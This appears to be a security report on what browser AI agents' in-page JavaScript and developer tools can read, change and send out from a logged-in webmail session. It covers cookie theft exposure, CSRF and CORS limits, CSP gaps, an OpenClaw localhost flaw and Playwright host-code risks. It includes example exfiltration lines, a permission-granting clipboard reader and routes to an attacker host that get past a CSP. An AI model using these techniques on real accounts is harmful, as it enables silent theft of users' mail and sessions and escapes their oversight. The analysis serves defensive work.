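HTTP Archive's *Cookies*, a chapter of its yearly report on the web, covers the million most popular sites in July 2025. Only 12% of first-party cookies, the ones belonging to the visited site, were marked HttpOnly, compared with just over 26% of cookies from other domains. W3Techs, a survey of the technologies that websites use, counts sites instead of cookies. It found HttpOnly cookies on 24.3% of all websites in June 2026 (W3Techs, 2026), up from 22.2% in August 2025 (W3Techs, 2025).

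Most cookies have nothing to do with logging in, so the 88% figure doesn't mean that 88% of sites leave their logins open. The most common first-party cookie in HTTP Archive's data belongs to Google Analytics, a visitor-counting service, and appears on about 60% of sites. Its script has to read the cookie, so the cookie can't be HttpOnly. *COOKIEGUARD* (2024), a study of how scripts share a site's cookies, found that third-party scripts had created 92% of the first-party cookies in its dataset. JavaScript can't create an HttpOnly cookie, so a large share of unmarked cookies is expected.

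Broad surveys can also miss important cookies, because a site may set them only after login. Rautenstrauch and colleagues compared 200 sites before and after logging in, and concluded that for some questions, looking only at the logged-out pages gives a badly skewed picture of security. They didn't measure HttpOnly, but the same problem applies, because a crawler that never logs in won't see many session cookies.

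The study by Calzavara and colleagues comes closest to showing how often a script on a page can read the cookies that keep a user logged in. Their software took shared usernames and passwords from BugMeNot, a public database, and tried them on popular sites. It then identified the login cookies by checking which ones each site needed to recognise the user. This succeeded on 6,124 sites. On 2,484 of them, or 41%, none of these cookies was HttpOnly, so a script on the page could have copied them all.

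Popular sites did no better. Of the 53 sampled sites in the top thousand, 29 had the problem. One example is the news site TechRepublic, which used a single authentication cookie. It protected the cookie against theft over the network but left it readable to scripts, and its pages included scripts from several other companies.

The figure comes from a list of sites that the researchers drew up in spring 2020, and practice may have improved since. It also leaves out the accounts where an agent could do the most damage, because people don't share bank or personal email passwords on BugMeNot. Banks and email providers may be more careful, but the study didn't cover those accounts.

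Chrome now has a safeguard against forgetting to mark a cookie HttpOnly. According to PPC Land's *Chrome 140 introduces HTTP cookie prefix to combat client side security threats*, the browser rejects a cookie whose name starts with `__Http` unless it is marked both HttpOnly and Secure. If a programmer gives a login cookie this prefix but leaves off HttpOnly, the login fails visibly instead of working with a cookie that page scripts can read. Sites may be slow to adopt the prefix, since HTTP Archive found that almost none use the older cookie prefixes after ten years.

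There is much less evidence about tokens in web storage. *Simple But Not Secure* (2024), a study of two-factor login, includes a table of vulnerable sites that marks those keeping the secret behind "remember this device" in `localStorage`. This shows that the practice exists, but not how common it is. Calzavara and colleagues searched `localStorage` for usernames, email addresses and passwords, and found at least one on 199 sites. On 48 of those sites, the data was still there after logout. They didn't count login tokens, so there is no figure comparable to the 41% for cookies.

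### Network lists and console messages

An agent often has developer tools besides JavaScript execution, and these can give the model data that page code can't read. Zenity Labs found two in Claude in Chrome. One, `read_network_requests`, lists the requests a tab has made, without their headers or bodies. The other reads the console, the browser's log of messages and errors. Zenity Labs warns that the network list can reveal login tokens, session identifiers and private IDs.

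The list omits headers and bodies, but the address of a request can still contain a secret. If the mail site downloads an attachment from `https://mail.example/file?token=eyJhbGci`, the list contains the token. Security guides advise against putting secrets in addresses, but some sites do it even with passwords. Calzavara and colleagues found that on four of their 6,124 sites, the login form put the password into the page's address, and the browser then passed the password on to other companies.

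Page code can already get some of these addresses by calling `performance.getEntriesByType("resource")`, which returns the addresses of scripts, images and other resources that the page has loaded. The network tool covers the whole tab, so its list should also include requests from the payment frame, which the same-origin policy hides from code in the inbox.

The missing headers matter because the browser sends `sid` in the `Cookie` header. A tool that returned complete request headers would give the model the session cookie, even though it is marked HttpOnly. A tool that returned response bodies could reveal the contents of the payment frame.

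The console tool can also read earlier console messages, which page code can't do. A script can only write to the console or, in the main world, replace `console.log` to catch later messages. Programmers sometimes log a whole server response while debugging and forget to remove the line. If the response contained an access token, the tool can read it in the log, even if the site keeps the token in a private variable that page code can't reach.

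Hackread's *Researchers Warn of Data Exposure Risks in Claude Chrome Extension*, a news report on Zenity's analysis, overstates the evidence. It describes technical tests in which the researchers read requests and logs and tricked Claude into running JavaScript. Zenity's own post bases its account of these tools on the list in the extension's system prompt, and the only test it illustrates is the unplanned visit to Wikipedia. The post supports the claim that the tools exist and could expose tokens, but it gives no example of Claude reading a token from a network list or a console.

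## What the code can change in the page, in storage and in the user's account

Code in the inbox can change almost anything that the mail site's own code can change. How much a change matters depends largely on how long it lasts:

| Where the change is | Examples in the mailbox | When it ends |
|---|---|---|
| The open page | a rewritten subject line, a new handler on the Send button | when the page reloads or the tab leaves it |
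| The browser's storage | a new `theme` cookie, an edited draft in `localStorage`, an extra record in IndexedDB | when a script or the user deletes it, or the cookie expires |
| The user's account | a sent email, a deleted message, a new forwarding address | when someone reverses it on the server, if that is possible |

### Changes to the open page

The code can add, remove and rewrite elements, fill in form fields, and attach event handlers, which are functions the browser runs in response to events such as clicks. The tool call may return within milliseconds, but the handlers and timers the code has set keep working. *OAuth 2.0 for Browser-Based Applications*, an Internet Engineering Task Force guide for programmers by Parecki, De Ryck and Waite, describes an attack in which a script copies the page's login tokens at a fixed interval, such as every ten seconds, so that the attacker always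 has the latest ones.

A reload would stop that timer. However, many mail services update a single page instead of loading new ones, so a user could move between inbox, drafts and settings all day without stopping anything the code had set up.

A temporary change can also have a permanent effect. If the code edits the recipient of an open draft and the user clicks Send without checking, the email goes to the wrong person.

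The agent's software can make page changes outlast a reload. Playwright's `addInitScript` function runs a given script each time a page is about to load. In Chromium, the DevTools protocol can add a function that the page calls to send text to the controlling program, and this function also survives reloads. The model's code can't call either command from inside the page, so they matter only if the agent's developer uses them or offers them as tools.

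### Changes to the browser's storage

The code can create, change and delete ordinary cookies and everything in `localStorage`, IndexedDB and Cache storage. It can't overwrite the HttpOnly cookie `sid`. If it sets a cookie for `mail.example` and its subdomains, the browser also sends that cookie to `login.mail.example`, whose pages the code can't access.

Stored data affects later visits because the site's scripts read it and act on it. If the mail service keeps an offline outbox in IndexedDB, a message the code adds there might go out the next time the site synchronises.

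The most powerful thing a site can leave in a browser is a service worker. This is a script that the browser keeps between visits and that can answer requests from the site's pages, including requests for the pages themselves. A hostile one could alter the mailbox at every visit. Registering one requires several things:

- The page must use `https`, or come from `localhost` during development.
- The worker must be a file on the page's own origin. The code can't register a string that the model has written.
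- The server must deliver the file as JavaScript, without redirecting to another address.
- The worker controls only pages in its own folder and below, unless the server sends a header that allows more.
- The page's Content Security Policy must allow the worker.

The main obstacle to installing a service worker is that its script must be a file on the site's own server, and in-page code can't normally put one there. It could do so if the mail site served attachments from its own origin and labelled them as JavaScript, but the worker would then control only the attachments folder. Many sites serve uploaded files from a separate domain, which prevents this.

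If the site already has a service worker, the code may not need to register another. Service workers often answer requests from Cache storage, and page code can replace the responses saved there. An altered copy of one of the site's scripts would then run on later visits until the site replaced it or the user cleared the site's data.

### How a script uses a login it can't read

The code can't read the session cookie, but it can send requests that carry it. To change a setting on the mail server, it needs only what the mail site's own scripts use:

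1. The code reads the anti-forgery token from the meta tag in the page.
2. It calls `fetch` with an address on `https://mail.example` and puts the token where the site's scripts would put it, often in a request header.
3. The browser attaches `sid`, because the request goes to the host that set the cookie.
4. The server finds a valid session and a matching token, and makes the change.
5. The browser passes the server's response back to the code, which can read it because the origins match.

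A service that requires an access token instead of a cookie is no better protected, because the code can attach the token from `localStorage` as the site's scripts do. In Chrome, code in an isolated world can make the same requests, because they also come from the page's origin.

Parecki and colleagues call this client hijacking. They write that the server can't distinguish such requests from those of the legitimate application, and that no security measure in the application can prevent them. Even the most secure design in their guide, which keeps all access tokens on a server and gives the browser only an HttpOnly cookie, doesn't prevent this attack. The design does prevent session hijacking, in which the attacker gets the session itself and can use it elsewhere.

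That argument is about malicious scripts, but it applies equally to a script that an agent runs with good intentions. The server receives the same request whether the user wanted the change, the model made a mistake, or hostile text on a page steered the model.

### Why SameSite cookies and anti-forgery tokens don't help

Most of the defences websites have against unwanted requests are designed to stop requests from other websites. In cross-site request forgery (CSRF), the attack they address, another site makes the user's browser send a request the user didn't intend. MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)* gives the example of a malicious page that, as soon as it loads, submits a hidden form to transfer 1,000 from the visitor's bank account to the attacker. If the visitor is logged in to the bank, the browser may attach the session cookie, and a bank without further checks would carry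 out the transfer.

The defences that MDN describes would work as follows for the mail service:

| Defence | Request from a malicious site | Request from code in the mailbox page |
|---|---|---|
| Anti-forgery token | lacks the token, because the malicious site can't read or guess it | includes the token |
| `Sec-Fetch-Site`, a header in which the browser reports where a request came from | header reads `cross-site` | header reads `same-origin` |
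| A required custom header, which other sites can't send without the server's permission | the browser blocks it | needs no permission |
| `SameSite=Strict` on the session cookie | the browser leaves out the cookie | the browser attaches the cookie |

All four checks correctly identify where the request came from. The request passes them because the code is running in the mail site's page.

Hiding or changing the token doesn't stop the agent's code from using it. PortSwigger's *XSS vs CSRF* explains that a script on a site can request the page that contains a valid token, read the token from the response, and use it. *S 4.403 Prevention of Cross-Site Request Forgery (CSRF, XSRF, Session Riding)*, an entry in a German government catalogue of security measures, suggests a new token for every request on sites with high protection needs, but a script can get each new token in the same way. Some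 sites keep the token in a cookie instead, but the site's scripts have to read that cookie, so the agent's code can read it too.

The security training organisation SANS concludes that a site must eliminate cross-site scripting before its CSRF protection can be fully effective. This advice is of little use to the site when the code comes from an agent's tool, because that code enters through the user's own software, not through a flaw in the site.

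### Two ways to change a forwarding address

Suppose the user asks the agent to forward all new mail to `archive@backup.example`. The agent could use the settings page, or it could send one request from the inbox with its JavaScript tool. The server ends up with the same setting, but the two methods leave different traces:

| | Settings page | One scripted request |
|---|---|---|
| What the user sees | the settings page opens, the address appears in a field, and the site confirms the change | the inbox, with nothing changed |
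| Agent's action log | separate entries for opening the page, typing the address and clicking Save | one JavaScript call and its result |
| Mail server's log | the settings page loads, then a change arrives from the user's session | a change arrives from the user's session |
| When the user can step in | between any two steps | before the call, if the software asks |

The JavaScript entry can be hard to interpret. A log of the full code would let a reviewer find the request, but it might not include the forwarding address, since the code could have read that from, for example, a message on the page. A list of network requests without their bodies, like the one in Claude in Chrome, would show that the code contacted the forwarding service but probably not which address it set. If the function returned only "done", the model would have no confirmation of the address either.

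Asking the user beforehand helps only if the question shows what will change. According to Zenity Labs, the plan that Claude in Chrome presents for approval contains only a list of sites and short descriptions of the intended actions, such as filling in a form. Both methods could fit the same plan, since both use only `mail.example`. Zenity Labs also warns that frequent approval requests may tempt users to switch to the mode that doesn't ask.

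The mail service might notify the user of the new forwarding address, but if the notice goes to the same mailbox, code running in the inbox page can delete it. Some services instead send a confirmation link to the new address, which catches typing errors but doesn't stop an attacker who owns the address.

Using the settings page leaves a readable record and gives the user several chances to notice a wrong address, but it isn't completely safe because the user may be looking at another tab.

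### What re-authentication and passkeys add

The code can supply everything the browser holds, so a server that needs stronger proof has to ask the user for something the browser doesn't hold. The German catalogue recommends that users log in again before critical actions such as a password change, so that these can't happen unnoticed. For sites with high protection needs, it recommends several proofs of identity, such as a one-time number or a chip card.

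How well this works depends on the proof:

- A password is weak if the browser fills it in automatically, because the code can then submit it.
- A one-time code sent by email fails in this case, because it arrives in the mailbox that the agent's code can read.
- A passkey is much stronger. This is a login key that a device or password manager keeps and uses only after the user approves, typically with a fingerprint, face scan or PIN. Page code can make the prompt appear, but it can't see the key or approve the prompt.

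Even a passkey can't prevent every unwanted change. The prompt shows the website's name but usually not the change, so a user who expects the agent to log in somewhere might approve a new forwarding address by mistake. Many sites also skip further prompts for several minutes after a successful one, and the code could send its request during that time. Protection is best when the server requires approval for each critical change and shows the details somewhere the page's code can't alter, such as an app on the user's phone.

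Parecki and colleagues discuss a similar trade-off for login tokens. A script can open the login server in a hidden frame and get a new token without the user noticing, if the user is still logged in there and the server allows silent logins. They write that requiring the user to interact each time would stop this but consider it impractical, because many applications log users in silently when they first load. Asking users for a fingerprint before they change a forwarding address is much less disruptive, since they rarely change one.

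### Scripted clicks and real user gestures

Browsers distinguish some scripted actions from real ones through `isTrusted`, a property of every event in a page. According to JetBrains' *isTrusted*, which reproduces MDN's definition, the value is `true` for events that the browser generates and `false` for a click that a script triggers with `click()`. A mail site could use this to ignore scripted clicks on its Delete button.

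Code can easily get past a site's `isTrusted` check. When the web developer Nadel compared real and scripted clicks on a form's submit button, the scripted click was untrusted, but the submit event that followed was trusted because the browser had generated it. A site that checked only the submit event would therefore accept the scripted submission. Code in the main world can also remove the site's check, or skip the button and send the request directly. The server receives no `isTrusted` value unless the site's own scripts report one, and the code could fake that report.

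An agent's separate click tool may not have this limit. The DevTools protocol has mouse and keyboard commands, and the browser marks the resulting events as trusted.

Some browser functions require a recent user gesture. MDN's *Transient activation* lists pressing a mouse button, lifting a finger from a touchscreen and pressing most keys as gestures that count. Moving the mouse or turning its wheel doesn't count. The permission expires after a short time, and some functions use it up. WebKit's *The User Activation API* gives the example of a page that opens the system's sharing menu, which uses up the gesture, and then can't open a new window. A few functions, such as playing audio, may need only one interaction at any time since the page loaded.

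Automation software can simulate the user gesture. In a command logged in a Mozilla bug report, Puppeteer requests a new window with the `userGesture` option turned on. That option is part of Chrome's protocol, but Firefox 121 added an equivalent for WebDriver BiDi, a newer automation standard for several browsers, according to Mozilla's *Add support for "userActivation" parameter to script evaluation*.

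So an agent developer can't rely on the gesture requirement to restrict the tool. Even when the requirement stops a script from opening a pop-up, the script can still delete every message in the user's mailbox, because `fetch` needs no gesture.

### Accidental damage

According to Zenity Labs, a browser agent could use the user's login to empty an inbox or stop every virtual machine in a cloud account. A small error in a script could be enough to cause either, even without an attacker.

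Suppose the user asks the agent to delete the newsletters from an inbox of 50 messages, six of which are newsletters. The page marks each message with the class `message` and each newsletter with the additional class `newsletter`. The model should select elements that have both:

```
.message.newsletter      matches 6 messages
.message, .newsletter    matches all 50
```

The comma means "or", so a loop that clicks Delete on every match would remove the whole inbox. An agent that deleted messages one at a time might make the same mistake, but it could notice after the first click that the wrong message was gone, whereas the script returns its result only after all 50 are deleted.

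A script can also delete the wrong message when its selector is correct, because some sites save memory by reusing the same row elements for different messages. When the script deletes one message, the others move up, and a row that held a newsletter when the loop began may now hold a message from the bank. A safer approach is to return the matching subject lines and message numbers first, then delete only those messages in a second call.

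Even a script meant only to read can change an account. For example, a script that checks a page for broken links might request every address on it. MDN advises sites not to make changes in response to GET requests, the type that browsers use to load pages, but some sites make them anyway. On such a site, the check could delete a message or cancel a subscription by requesting the link that does so.

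Other accidents come from scripts that don't finish. An endless loop can freeze the page, so the user can't click anything to stop it. OpenClaw's developers, who work on an AI agent project, planned to give page scripts a time budget and a separate connection to the browser, so that the scripts wouldn't share Playwright's command queue for the page. Chromium has an experimental `timeout` setting that ends a script after a given number of milliseconds. But stopping a script doesn't undo what it has already done, so the inbox may be left with 20 messages deleted and 30 remaining.

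Chromium also has an experimental setting called `throwOnSideEffect`, which stops the code with an error if the browser can't rule out that the code will change something. This could stop the deletion loop at its first click. It could also reject harmless code whose effects the browser can't determine, and it doesn't help when the user wants something deleted.

Whether the user can undo the damage depends mostly on the site. Reloading the page fixes a damaged display, and many mail services keep deleted messages in a trash folder for some time. If the loop had clicked Reply and Send instead of Delete, it would have sent 50 emails that the user probably couldn't take back.

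## Which servers the code can reach, and whose answers it can read

Code in the inbox at `https://mail.example` can send the text of a message to almost any server on the internet. The same-origin policy mainly stops the code from reading what a server at another origin sends back. Anthropic's warning about `javascript_exec` mentions requests to the page's own origin, which readers could easily mistake for a limit on which servers the code can contact.

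Documentation often blurs this difference. According to the introduction of MDN's *Cross-Origin Resource Sharing (CORS)*, code that uses `fetch` can only request resources from its own origin unless the response from the other origin includes the right headers. But the browser has to send a request before it can receive those headers, as later parts of the same page make clear.

### A cross-origin request step by step

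CORS is a set of response headers by which a server lets scripts of other origins read its answers. The rules are in the Fetch Standard from WHATWG, a group that maintains many of the web's core standards. Suppose code in the inbox runs this line:

```
fetch("https://stats.example/log", { method: "POST", body: "Lunch on Friday?" })
```

1. The browser checks the page's Content Security Policy (CSP). If the policy doesn't allow connections to `stats.example`, the request ends here.
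2. The browser decides whether it must ask the server before sending. Here it needn't, because an ordinary web form could send the same kind of request.
3. The browser adds the header `Origin: https://mail.example`. It leaves out any cookies for `stats.example`, because the code didn't ask for them.
4. The server receives the subject line and can store it.
5. The server answers. The browser looks for the header `Access-Control-Allow-Origin`, which must contain either `https://mail.example` or `*`, meaning any origin.
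6. If the header matches, the code can read the answer. Otherwise `fetch` fails with an error.

The server receives the subject line in step 4, whatever happens in steps 5 and 6. CORS therefore doesn't prevent exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone who isn't authorised to have it. An attacker who owns the receiving server can also send the header that lets the code read its answers.

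The error in step 6 can mislead an agent. According to MDN, the code can detect only that an error occurred, and the reason appears in the browser's console. The error alone doesn't show whether the request was never sent, or whether the server carried it out and the browser blocked the code from reading the answer.

### What a preflight prevents

The browser needs the server's permission before it sends some requests, such as those that use the DELETE method, carry a custom header or have a JSON body. It first sends a short request called a preflight, which lists the method and headers the code has specified. The preflight never carries cookies. The browser sends the real request only if the server's response allows it.

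Web forms could send data to any origin long before `fetch` existed, so servers already had to protect themselves against unwanted form submissions. Browsers therefore let scripts send form-like requests freely, but check with the server before sending requests that a form couldn't make.

A preflight protects the receiving server from unexpected changes, but it does little to keep the mailbox's contents private. Code can avoid the preflight by sending plain text instead of JSON. Even a refused preflight can leak data, because the browser sends the preflight to the full address of the intended request, including anything the code put after the question mark.

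Servers can also reject form-like requests by checking where they came from, for example with the `Sec-Fetch-Site` header. *Fetch Me If You Can* (2026), a study of sites that check this and related headers, found 196 websites, mostly vBulletin forums, that block all POST requests from other sites. Another 41 websites reject requests that come from image elements. These checks protect accounts on the servers that use them, but they don't help the mail user, because an attacker's server would accept every request.

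### Cookies and the right to read the answer

By default, `fetch` sends no cookies to other origins. The code can request them with `credentials: "include"`, but the browser still applies its cookie rules. `login.mail.example` belongs to the same site as the inbox, so the browser attaches even `SameSite=Strict` cookies. `pay.example` is a different site, so Chrome would attach only cookies that `pay.example` has marked `SameSite=None`, and only if the user hasn't blocked third-party cookies.

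Asking for cookies also makes it harder to read the answer:

| CORS headers in the server's answer | Readable without `include`? | Readable with `include`? |
|---|---|---|
| none | no | no |
| `Access-Control-Allow-Origin: *` | yes | no |
| `Access-Control-Allow-Origin: https://mail.example` | yes | no |
| the same, plus `Access-Control-Allow-Credentials: true` | yes | yes |

The browser applies the table strictly, so if the server writes `True` with a capital letter, the code can't read the answer. This is meant to stop a server from accidentally giving away personal data, because an answer to a request with cookies may contain the user's account details. WHATWG calls the combination in the last row "rather unsafe" and urges server developers to take extreme care with it.

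The code can also send a request with the option `mode: "no-cors"`, which gives up access to the answer. It then gets an opaque response, which shows status 0, no headers and no body, even if the server answered normally. Opaque responses look almost the same as network errors, so an agent shouldn't take status 0 as proof that nothing arrived.

This mode works the way images did before CORS existed, when a page could display a picture from another site but couldn't examine its contents. In wording proposed for the Fetch Standard in 2025, Rosenthal explains that browsers still support such requests for compatibility, and that they restrict what the page may do with the response instead of restricting network access.

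### Other ways for data to leave a page

A script can send data without `fetch` by adding an image to the page whose address contains private text. The browser will send that text to the image's server, whether or not the server returns a picture.

CSP is the main browser mechanism that lets a site limit these routes. It consists of directives, each of which lists the permitted servers for one kind of traffic:

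| Way out | Where the data travels | CSP directive that limits it |
|---|---|---|
| `fetch` and similar commands | address, headers or body | `connect-src` |
| WebSocket, a lasting two-way connection | messages | `connect-src` |
| Image | address | `img-src` |
| Script, stylesheet or font | address | `script-src`, `style-src` or `font-src` |
| Embedded frame | address | `frame-src` |
| Form submission | form fields or address | `form-action` |
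| Moving the tab to another page or opening a new window | address | none |
| WebRTC, the direct connections used for video calls | connection details or messages | none in common use |

If a site leaves out a directive whose name ends in `-src`, the browser falls back on the general rule `default-src`. `form-action` has no such fallback. If a site sets `default-src 'self'`, which permits only its own origin, but not `form-action`, its pages can still submit forms to any server.

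Drafts of the CSP standard once included a navigation directive, `navigate-to`, but later versions dropped it. A script can therefore always send the tab to an address that contains private data. The user may notice that the inbox has disappeared, but only after the data has been sent.

CSP also doesn't check what the code sends to a permitted server. `www.google-analytics.com` is among the five hosts that policies name most often, according to the *Security* chapter of HTTP Archive's 2025 report on the web. Anyone can open a Google Analytics account, so a policy that permits this host may also let code send data to a stranger's account. Code in the inbox can also email the data to someone, because the mail server is a permitted destination. None of these checks apply to the text that a function returns to the model.

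### How many sites limit outgoing traffic

About a fifth of websites have a Content Security Policy (CSP). HTTP Archive puts the share at 21.9%, up from 18.5% a year earlier. In *10 years of watching the web*, Report URI, which sells CSP monitoring, gives a similar share of 20.8% for popular sites (170,057 of the 819,002 that responded on 13 June 2026). CSPs are more common among the most popular sites. A crawl of the top 10,000 sites in September 2026 for *Privacy-Friendly Cohort Determination* (2026), which proposes an advertising system, found an enforced policy on 33.7% of the 7,969 it could reach.

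Many of these policies don't limit where data can go. According to HTTP Archive, the six most common complete policies account for about 66% of all CSP headers on mobile pages, and none of the six names permitted destinations. Five only tell the browser to use encrypted connections, stop other sites from showing the page in a frame, or both. The sixth restricts how scripts insert text into the page.

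Most figures on policy strictness concern scripts. Report URI found the keyword `unsafe-inline`, which permits scripts written directly into a page, in 46.8% of policies, and `unsafe-eval`, which permits `eval`, in 41.9%. HTTP Archive's figures are higher, at 92% and 77%, but cover only policies with rules for scripts. These keywords make it easier for an attacker to inject a script. They matter less for an agent's tool, because the DevTools protocol can run the model's code even under a strict policy.

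The September crawl comes closer to measuring outgoing traffic. It checked whether each site's policy would allow a frame from a server the site had no reason to list. 88.8% of the sites would allow it, so a script there could send data out in the frame's address. The share was 86.8% on a separate list of business, technology and news sites. The crawler visited only front pages and didn't log in, so these figures may not hold for an inbox or a bank account page.

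### WebSockets and the Origin header

A WebSocket is a connection that stays open so that a page and a server can exchange messages, for example in a chat. It starts with a web request called a handshake. Browsers don't apply CORS to this request, so they send no preflight and don't check the server's response for CORS headers. If the server accepts the connection, the page's code can send messages and read the answers.

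The server itself has to refuse connections from unfamiliar websites. It can do this by checking the `Origin` header, which the browser includes in the handshake and page code can't change. The browser may also attach the user's cookies, so if a server recognises users by their cookies but ignores `Origin`, another website could act as the user and read the results.

The same applies to programs on the user's own computer. Many of them listen at `127.0.0.1` (localhost, or the loopback address), which only programs on the same machine, including the browser, can reach. Browsers block web requests to certain ports used by other services, such as 22 for remote login and 25 for email, but allow requests to most others.

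### The OpenClaw gateway flaw

OpenClaw is an open-source assistant that runs on the user's computer, connects to messaging apps, calendars and files, and can execute commands. Its central program, the gateway, is a WebSocket server that listens on the loopback address by default. Luz (2026), in *Your Browser Is a Backdoor to Your AI Agent*, reported that a website could take control of the gateway if the user merely visited it. Luz, who works for the security company Oasis, traced the flaw to three design decisions:

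- The gateway checked the `Origin` header only for connections that identified themselves as its web dashboard or chat widget. The developers thought the check unnecessary for other kinds of client, since these don't normally run in a browser.
- It treated every connection from the same computer as trustworthy, and approved new devices from there without asking the user.
- It didn't limit the number of password attempts from the same computer.

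All three rest on the assumption that a local connection comes from the user's own software. But a website's script also runs on the user's computer, inside the browser, so its connection looks the same as a local app's at the network level. Only the `Origin` header identifies the website.

OpenClaw's security team rated the flaw as high severity and released a fix, version 2026.2.25, within 24 hours of the report. Randolph Barr of the security company Cequence said in Security Boulevard's *Latest OpenClaw Flaw Can Let Malicious Websites Hijack Local AI Agents* that automatic device pairing and similar conveniences had sped up adoption but weakened the product's defences.

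An earlier OpenClaw flaw let a page do harm without reading any answers. According to Rapid7's vulnerability database, versions before 2026.2.14 accepted ordinary web requests from any site to the local service that controls OpenClaw's browser. A hostile site could open tabs, start or stop the browser, and change cookies and stored data. The flaw's entry has a severity score of 7.1 out of 10, with a high impact on data integrity and none on confidentiality. Fixed versions reject requests for such changes when the headers show that they came from another website.

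In both cases the threat was a malicious website, but code that an agent runs in a page can make the same connections. The tool can't start programs on the computer directly. If a local service starts them on request, the user's protection depends on how well that service checks its callers.

### Chrome's Local Network Access prompt

Browsers have begun to ask the user before a website connects to local addresses, a feature Chrome calls Local Network Access. *Intent to Ship* (Thompson, 2025), Google's notice of the plan, defines a local network request as one from a public website to a local or loopback address, or from a local website to a loopback address. A public address works from anywhere on the internet, while a local address such as `192.168.0.1` works only within one network and often belongs to a router.

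Local network access restrictions are meant to stop websites from attacking devices that trust their own network. MDN's *Local network access* gives the example of a site that changes the settings of a visitor's router so that later visits to other websites lead to fakes. The attacker can do this without reading the router's answer, and the attack is easier because many people never change the router's default password.

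Chrome added the prompt in version 142, in October 2025. The University of Illinois help page for staff and students, *Google Chrome Local Network Access Permission*, gives its wording as "Look for and connect to any device on your local network", with buttons to allow or block. At first the prompt covered `fetch` and resources such as images, but not WebSockets, so it would not have stopped the attack on OpenClaw's gateway that Luz described in February 2026.

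Chrome has since closed this gap. *Intent to Ship* (Chromestatus, 2026) proposed extending the prompt to WebSockets in version 147. Hubert Chao, one of the Google developers who proposed the change, reported that Chrome's usage counter for local WebSocket connections was at roughly 0.1%, probably inflated by sites that use such connections to detect fraud. Visualware (2026), which makes network testing software affected by the change, confirms that it was in the stable version by April 2026. The restriction also applies to Edge, Brave, Opera and other browsers built on Chromium.

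Some routes may still be open:

- The specification also covers WebRTC and WebTransport, a newer kind of two-way connection. Luz reported in February that Chrome didn't yet ask about either, and the WebSocket announcement doesn't mention them.
- The specification covers frames that load a local address, but its list doesn't include moving the whole tab to one.
- A page on a company's internal network can contact other devices on that network without a prompt, because the definition covers only its requests to the loopback address.
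- Android apps that display web pages through the WebView component don't have the feature.

Luz wrote that Firefox had begun to introduce its own prompt, which also covered WebSockets, but had turned it on by default only for users of its strict tracking protection. Safari had no prompt, but it blocked unencrypted WebSocket connections from encrypted pages, even those to the user's own computer.

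The permission also belongs to the website, not to the code that makes the request. If the user lets the mail site connect to a local printer, code that an agent runs in the inbox can use the same permission while it lasts. Company administrators can set the permission in advance for particular sites, and then the user isn't asked.

### Four destinations from the mailbox

Suppose the mail service sends this policy with the inbox:

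```
default-src 'self';
script-src 'self' https://stats.example;
connect-src 'self' https://stats.example;
frame-src https://pay.example
```

The visitor-counting server `stats.example` lets every origin read its answers, and the payment server `pay.example` sends no CORS headers. `collect.example` belongs to an attacker. A program on the user's computer accepts WebSocket connections from any page on port 9000. In a current version of Chrome, code in the main world could reach them as follows:

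| Destination | Without a CSP | With this policy |
|---|---|---|
| `https://stats.example` | receives data, and the code can read the answer if it doesn't ask for cookies | the same |
| `https://pay.example` | receives data, but the code can't read the answer | receives data through a frame, a form or navigation, but the code can't read the answer |
| `https://collect.example` | receives data, and the code can read the answer if the attacker allows it | receives data through a form, navigation or WebRTC, and the code can read answers only over WebRTC |
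| `ws://127.0.0.1:9000` | receives data if the user allows the connection, and the code can then read the answer | can't receive WebSocket messages, even if the user allows the connection |

The page's content security policy blocks `fetch` requests and WebSocket connections to the attacker's server, `collect.example`, but code can still send a stolen message there through a form submission, navigation or WebRTC. WebRTC also lets the server send data back. Adding `form-action 'self'` would block the form submission but not navigation or WebRTC. A `fetch` request to `collect.example` would go through if the code ran in a Chrome extension's isolated world, where the page's `connect-src` rule doesn't apply.

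## How page code differs from code running on the host

Code in the inbox at `https://mail.example` can try to contact a program on the user's computer, but it can't start a program or open a file by its path. Host code execution, which means running code as a process on the machine, has neither restriction. Playwright MCP has a tool of each kind, and calls to them can look almost the same:

```
browser_evaluate { function: "() => document.title" }
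browser_run_code_unsafe { code: "async (page) => await page.title()" }
```

`browser_evaluate` and `browser_run_code_unsafe` can both return the page's title. `browser_evaluate` runs its function inside the page, while `browser_run_code_unsafe` runs its function in the Playwright server, an ordinary program outside the browser. The function in the server controls the page through the `page` object.

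### What browser_run_code_unsafe can do

Playwright's manual warns that `browser_run_code_unsafe` is "RCE-equivalent". RCE (remote code execution) means that an outsider can run code of their choice on someone else's machine. The warning is fair because the server has the rights of the account that started it. The model's code may therefore be able to read that account's files, start programs and connect to any server. The same-origin policy and the site's Content Security Policy don't apply to this code.

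The examples in the manual use only a small part of this power. Three of them do something to the browser that page code can't do:

- One gives the page permission to read the clipboard and returns the text there, which might be a password that the user has just copied.
- Another gives the page permission to use the device's location, then sets that location to a point in San Francisco.
- A third reads the total inside a payment frame and returns "$49.99".

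The clipboard example uses both environments. This is a shortened version with comments:

```
async (page) => {
  // runs in the server process
  await page.context().grantPermissions(["clipboard-read"]);
  // the inner function runs in the page
  return await page.evaluate(() => navigator.clipboard.readText());
}
```

The server first tells the browser to allow clipboard reading without prompting the user for permission. The inner function then runs in the page, just as code from `browser_evaluate` would. The example doesn't name a website, so the permission probably covers every site the agent opens in the same browser session.

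In the payment frame example, Playwright gets around a different limit. Page code in the mailbox got `null` when it tried to access the document in the frame from `https://pay.example`. Playwright instead runs separate code inside the frame, with the frame's own origin. The same-origin policy doesn't block this, because no script reads across the boundary. The data from the two origins is combined only in the server.

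All three examples need control of the browser, but none needs the host's files or programs. Of two other examples, one reads the text "3 items left" from a to-do list, and the other waits for a loading indicator to disappear. Page code could do both, unless the wait has to continue while a new page loads. A developer who turns on `browser_run_code_unsafe` for any of these tasks also lets the model run code on the host.

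The host may not be the user's own machine, since the Playwright server can run on a different computer from the browser. If the server runs on a disposable virtual machine that holds nothing of value, code running on the host may do the user little harm.

### Four levels of access

Browser extensions and CDP clients have more power than page code but less than a host process. A CDP client is a program that controls the browser through the Chrome DevTools Protocol. The table compares what code at each level can normally do:

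| | Page code | Extension | CDP client | Host process |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| HttpOnly cookies | can use them in requests but can't read them | can read them for sites it has access to, with the `cookies` permission | can read all of them | can often get them through the browser or its profile folder |
| Other origins | can send requests but usually can't read the answers | can read pages on sites it has access to | can read and change any page | can contact any server, but without the user's logins |
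| Browser permissions, such as location | can ask the user, and can use what the site already has | can change some site settings, with a special permission | can grant them without a prompt | doesn't need them, but may need the operating system's permission |
| Local files | only files the user picks | `file://` pages, if the user allows it | can open them as `file://` pages | any file that its account can open |
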